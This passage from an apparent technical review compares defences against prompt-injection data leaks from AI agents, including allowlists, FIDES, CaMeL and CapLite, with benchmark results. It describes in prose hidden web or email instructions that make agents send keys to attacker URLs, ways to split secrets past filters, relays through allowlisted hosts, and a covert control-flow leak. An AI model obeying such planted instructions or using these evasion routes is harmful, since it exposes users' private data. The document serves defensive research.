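Anthropic's fix in the Claude app has a similar drawback, since Claude can no longer read a manual by following its links from chapter to chapter. dyb proposes letting Claude follow links only on sites that the user names in the conversation. Claude could then read the manual after one extra confirmation, but a user who named a site like Paul's would still be exposed.

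## How allowlists compare with controls on the data itself

Domain allowlists and exact-URL checks allow or block a request based on its address. Other controls track private data and block a request based on what the assistant has read, regardless of the destination. Researchers have tested both approaches, but rarely against an attacker who could use an allowlisted host.

### A test with the attacker off the list

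In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) compared several defences on one agent they built. The agent fetches any web page its user mentions and adds the page's title, description and text to the model's context. It used Qwen2.5 7B, a small model, running on their own computer. The user always asked for a summary of a page, and the page contained instructions to send an API key to the attacker's server in a URL parameter. The key was already in the model's context.

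The researchers varied where the page held its instructions, whether the assistant reached the page through a redirect, and whether it sent the key whole or in four pieces. The attacker's server received a request in 423 of 480 runs (88%). In 95% of the successful attacks, the reply the user saw looked harmless. The assistant never contacted the server in 120 runs with ordinary pages.

The success rate depends heavily on the model. In *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*, Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025) tried 1,068 versions of a similar attack on each model they tested. Success ranged from 0% for six models to 72.4% for Grok 4. They used no defences outside the model, so their study does not measure network controls.

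Splitting the key reduced the share of runs in which the first request contained sensitive data from 96.7% to 26.3%, a relative drop of 73%. The attacker's server still received something in about 77% of the runs with a split key, compared with 99% of the others, so the drop does not mean that 73% less data got out. The measure is also unreliable. By the researchers' definition, any piece of the key counts as a leak, so the figure for the first three requests should be at least as high as the figure for the first one, but it is only 15.8%. Splitting can hide a secret from a filter that looks for complete keys, but it doesn't help an attacker get past a domain allowlist, because every piece must still be sent to an allowed host.

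The researchers then tested defences in 30 runs each, with the whole key and a page that the assistant opened directly:

| Defence | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Instructions telling the model to treat web text as data | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web text as untrusted | 100% |
| Both the instructions and the tags | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 0% |
| "Redirect detection" | 0% |
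| Filter for words such as "password" or "token" in the URL | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking parameters | 0% |

The allowlist contained three of a company's own hosts and `example.com`. Lan and colleagues deliberately gave the attacker a domain outside it, `evil-collector.net`, and the attacker had no account or relay on any of the four allowed hosts. The result shows that an allowlist blocks a host that isn't on it, even when the model has obeyed the attacker. This is an advantage over a warning in the prompt, which the model can ignore. But the test doesn't show how well an allowlist resists the bypasses in ChatGPT, Copilot or Superhuman, all of which went through allowed hosts. Lan and colleagues acknowledge that attackers could use open redirects, abandoned subdomains or compromised sites.

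The result for redirects is weaker still, because these runs involved no redirect. The "redirect detection" was a filter that rejected bare IP addresses, certain domain endings, and paths containing words such as "steal" or "collect". The attacker's address in the paper's examples ends in `/collect`, so renaming that page might have gotten it past the filter.

Without defences, the model tried to send the key in every run, but it tried in only 23% of runs with the word filter and in none with the filter for random-looking parameters. This is odd because a filter that inspects finished requests should not change how often the model tries. The researchers suggest that the model avoids random-looking parameters when a filter is active, but they don't explain how it would detect the filter.

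### Judgements in the EchoLeak paper

Reddy and Gujral set eight defences against six parts of the EchoLeak attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot and marked which parts each defence would stop. They call the table theoretical in its caption and state in their limitations section that they ran no experiments, although they refer to "our tests" in the text. All the marks are therefore judgements, though evidence from other attacks bears on several of them.

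| Defence | Expected to stop the zero-click leak? | Evidence from elsewhere |
|---|---|---|
| URL allowlist | Yes | EchoLeak went through a host on Copilot's list |
| Strict Content Security Policy | Yes | Copilot's policy allowed a host with a relay |
| Proxy that loads only signed image addresses | Yes | CamoLeak spelled out secrets through GitHub's signed proxy |
| Human approval | Yes | People may approve requests without understanding them |
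| Marking outside text as untrusted | No | Tags made no difference in the *Silent Egress* runs |
| Using only internal sources by default | No | The paper's own text contradicts this |
| Restricting the format of replies | No | Copilot's link filter missed one Markdown notation |
| Monitoring outgoing requests | No | Splitting a secret can hide it from a filter |

The proxy would be a little harder to bypass than one would expect from CamoLeak, because Reddy and Gujral propose signatures that expire. An attacker who had collected signed addresses in advance would have to keep replacing them.

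The paper's table seems to undervalue restricting Copilot to internal sources when it answers questions about internal projects. If Copilot never used email from unknown outside senders for those answers, it would not read the attacker's instructions alongside the company's secrets. The paper says elsewhere that EchoLeak would then fail "by design". Unlike an allowlist, which limits where requests can go, this defence limits which data Copilot reads together.

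### Cutting access when private and untrusted text meet

The simplest controls remove a channel through which data can leak. GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat, and OpenAI's Lockdown Mode restricts several features. However, turning off images does not stop an agent that can open web pages from leaking data through their URLs.

A more selective rule blocks network access only once the assistant has both private data and untrusted text in its context. Suppose Marta's assistant has read her mailbox, including the newsletter with the hidden instructions. The software then blocks every outgoing request, so the model can't send the alarm code to the attacker's own site or to a storage account on an allowed host. Marta still gets her summary, because writing it doesn't require a request.

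The drawback is that the assistant can no longer look up the train mentioned in one of her emails. If every conversation includes private memories of her, even an ordinary web search becomes difficult, because the first page the assistant reads is untrusted text and the software would then block it from opening a second.

To allow more tasks, the software has to identify which pieces of data are private or untrusted, instead of treating the whole conversation as both.

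### Labelling data with FIDES

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and carries them along whenever a program copies or combines it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a version built at Microsoft for AI agents. Each piece of data has an integrity label, either trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label, which can list the people allowed to read it. Anything made from several pieces is untrusted if any of them is, and only people allowed to read all of them may read it. If Marta and Jonas may read one email, and Marta and a supplier may read another, only Marta may read a text based on both.

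Suppose Marta asks the assistant to summarise her unread mail and send the summary to Jonas, a colleague. FIDES can do this without showing the mail to the main model, which chooses the tools:

| Step | Label of the result |
|---|---|
| Marta makes her request | Trusted, public |
| A tool reads the mail, and FIDES stores it under the name `mail` | Untrusted, private |
| A second model, which has no tools, summarises `mail`, and FIDES stores the result as `summary` | Untrusted, private |
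| The main model asks to send `summary` to Jonas | Trusted choice of tool and recipient, untrusted and private text |

The main model sees only the names `mail` and `summary`. The newsletter can make the second model write a bad summary, but it can't change the recipient or add another action. FIDES can therefore allow the message under a rule that requires only the tool and recipient to come from trusted text.

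A strict confidentiality rule would still block the action, because Jonas was not a recipient of every email. Costa and colleagues point out that a system may waive this rule when the action comes from a trusted context, because it assumes the user intended to share the data.

Now suppose the main model opens `mail` to decide what to do next. Its context becomes untrusted and private. If it then follows the newsletter's instructions and tries to open `https://newsletter-art.storage.example/banner.png?ref=7315`, FIDES detects that untrusted text influenced the request and that the address contains private data. Either can be enough to block the request, even though a domain allowlist would have approved the host.

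The confidentiality rule works only if it correctly specifies who can read what each host receives. A developer who believed that only the office could read requests to the storage company would make the same mistake as with an allowlist. The rule about untrusted text would still block the request in this example.

FIDES also leaves a gap for image leaks because, in its standard form, it checks tool calls but treats the reply to the user as harmless. If `summary` contained the attacker's image and the assistant displayed it to Marta, her browser would request the image without a tool call. Costa and colleagues note that a developer can check replies as well. A chat window that shows images would need that check or would have to turn images off for replies based on private data.

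### Security and completed tasks

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks in four simulated settings and a set of planted attacks. With GPT-4o as the model, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent. When FIDES ran without its policy checks, 21 succeeded, because the main model could still open the hidden text and follow instructions in it. None succeeded with the checks on.

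The researchers also added labels and checks to the ordinary agent without hiding any data from its model. The modified agent loses access to many tools once it reads untrusted text, so its results roughly indicate how much cutting access reduces the share of tasks completed. The table shows that share for each agent when there was no attack.

| Setting | Ordinary agent, no checks | Ordinary agent, with checks | FIDES, with checks |
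|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |
| Average | 84.3% | 41.9% | 50.0% |

Checks alone halved the number of completed tasks. Hiding untrusted text recovered about a fifth of the loss, and more with a better model. With OpenAI's o1, FIDES completed 16 percentage points more tasks than the ordinary agent with checks. With GPT-4o, FIDES did worse on travel tasks because many travel tools were allowed to run on untrusted text anyway, and the model worked poorly with data hidden from it.

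Some of the lost tasks are ones no such system should complete. Several banking tasks, for example, ask the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which is also how a prompt injection works.

### CaMeL and its successors

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025, fixes the plan before the agent reads anything. A privileged model sees only the user's request and writes a short program. For Marta's request it might be:

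```
mail = read_unread_mail()
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise this mail", mail)
send_message("Jonas", summary)
```

A special interpreter runs the program, tracks where each value came from and checks a policy before each tool call. A hostile email that reaches the quarantined model can change only the value of a variable such as `summary`, according to *CaMeLoT* (2026), a later system based on CaMeL.

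The fixed plan is also CaMeL's main limitation, because the program has to anticipate everything the mail might require. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) measured the resulting drop in performance on AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks for teams of agents. Using CaMeL in each agent lowered task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by only 13.4 points for the two strongest, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5.

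They also found that attacks on a group of agents could still succeed when each agent was protected separately. One agent put text from a database into its instructions to another, which treated the whole message as a trusted request and emailed private data to an outsider. The researchers fixed this by sending instructions and data through separate channels. In their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded in 12.9% of cases without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and none with the fix. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without these defences, so the benchmark may be too easy for comparing defences on the newest models.

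These tests ran without CaMeL's data policies, so they measured whether attackers could change an agent's actions, not whether private data could reach the wrong place. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) report in *The LLMbda Calculus* that turning the policies on halved the share of AgentDojo banking tasks that CaMeL completed.

*CapLite* (Xu, Liu and Nakayama, 2026) reports the most direct test of URL leaks. Planted text told agents to fetch an attacker's URL with a tool that only reads pages. Across eight open models, the attack succeeded in 85 of 168 attempts without a defence and in none with either CaMeL or the paper's own system, also called CapLite. CapLite opens a URL only if the user's request contains it. This rule is stricter than OpenAI's or Anthropic's exact-URL checks because it excludes URLs from search results.

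CapLite does not have the model write its own security rules, which small models do badly. On one of the 15 models in the study, CaMeL's programs failed to run in 68% of attempts. But even when there was no attack, CapLite completed only 28.1% of tasks, compared with 59.4% for an undefended agent and 24.9% for CaMeL. CapLite also does not restrict the body of a message. If the messaging program loads images, an attacker might still get data out through an image in a message to a recipient the user named.

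Computing costs vary widely among these defences. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) tested CaMeL and FIDES on 17 tasks for agents that operate a computer through its screen. CaMeL used 64% more input tokens than an undefended agent and cost $5.40 in model fees. FIDES used about 29 times as many input tokens as the undefended agent and cost $76.07. CapLite used fewer tokens than an undefended agent in its own tests.

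*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) aims to keep more tasks possible after an agent encounters untrusted text. A temporary copy of the agent reads the text and returns only an answer in a restricted format, so the original agent can keep using its tools. The system completed 64.2% to 91% of tasks, and no attack succeeded in 1,320 protected runs. These figures come from different benchmarks than those for FIDES, so they don't show how much better the method is.

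### Leaks that labels miss

Labels can fail when a program's choices reveal a secret. Garby and colleagues found a case in CaMeL that works like this. A program starts with two public values, A and B, both set to "yes". If Marta's alarm code begins with 7, the program changes A to "no". If A is still "yes", it changes B to "no". If B is still "yes", it sends a request, which happens only when the code begins with 7.

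The program therefore sends the request only if the code begins with 7. In that case it skips the step that would have changed B, so CaMeL never marks B as private and allows the request. An attacker would still have to get CaMeL's privileged model to write such a program, which is hard because that model doesn't read outside text.

The software around CaMeL's interpreter has another leak, because it runs a program again after a failure. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and repeated attempts can reveal the rest.

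FIDES has a similar limit by design. It stops private data from flowing directly into a request, but an attacker who sees which tools the agent uses, and in what order, may still learn something about that data. Costa and colleagues considered a stronger standard, noninterference, but found it too restrictive because after reading a secret, the agent could use almost no tools with publicly visible effects.

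Garby and colleagues instead designed a small programming language for agents and gave a computer-checked proof that every program written in it satisfies a form of noninterference. The guarantee does not cover what an attacker can learn from whether a program finishes. Their agent completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did without its policies, and it resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

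### Allowlists as one layer

An allowlist is still useful alongside labels, because labels protect only data that someone has labelled correctly, and only in software that tracks them. If Marta's alarm code were in a note that the office had marked as public, FIDES could let it leave, but an allowlist would still stop the assistant from sending it directly to the attacker's server. An allowlist also takes little compute, needs no second model, and gives the same result however persuasive the newsletter is.

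The two controls can also work together. A developer could let an agent fetch public documentation from many hosts but send private data only to hosts whose readers are already allowed to see it. The list for private data would then be much shorter and easier to review.

Attackers adapt to layered defences, which is the main objection to relying on them. If an allowlist and a prompt-injection classifier each stop 90% of a fixed set of attacks, and their failures are independent, only 1% of the attacks will get past both. But an attacker who can test against both will keep trying until an attack gets past them, then reuse it. Aim's researchers got EchoLeak past three of Microsoft's defences this way.

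Attackers can get around an allowlist fairly easily once someone has found a suitable host, because the same relay works against every customer with the same list until the vendor closes it. Finding another host does not help against data labels, because the check blocks private data from going there too. The attacker has to find a secret with the wrong label, a request that avoids the check, or an error in the tracking. The work on CaMeL shows that these flaws exist, but each may be specific to one system.

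Lan and colleagues' comparison would be fairer if the attacker had an account on one of the listed hosts. The allowlist would then probably offer no protection in their setup, because the model tried to send the key in all 30 runs with the allowlist on.
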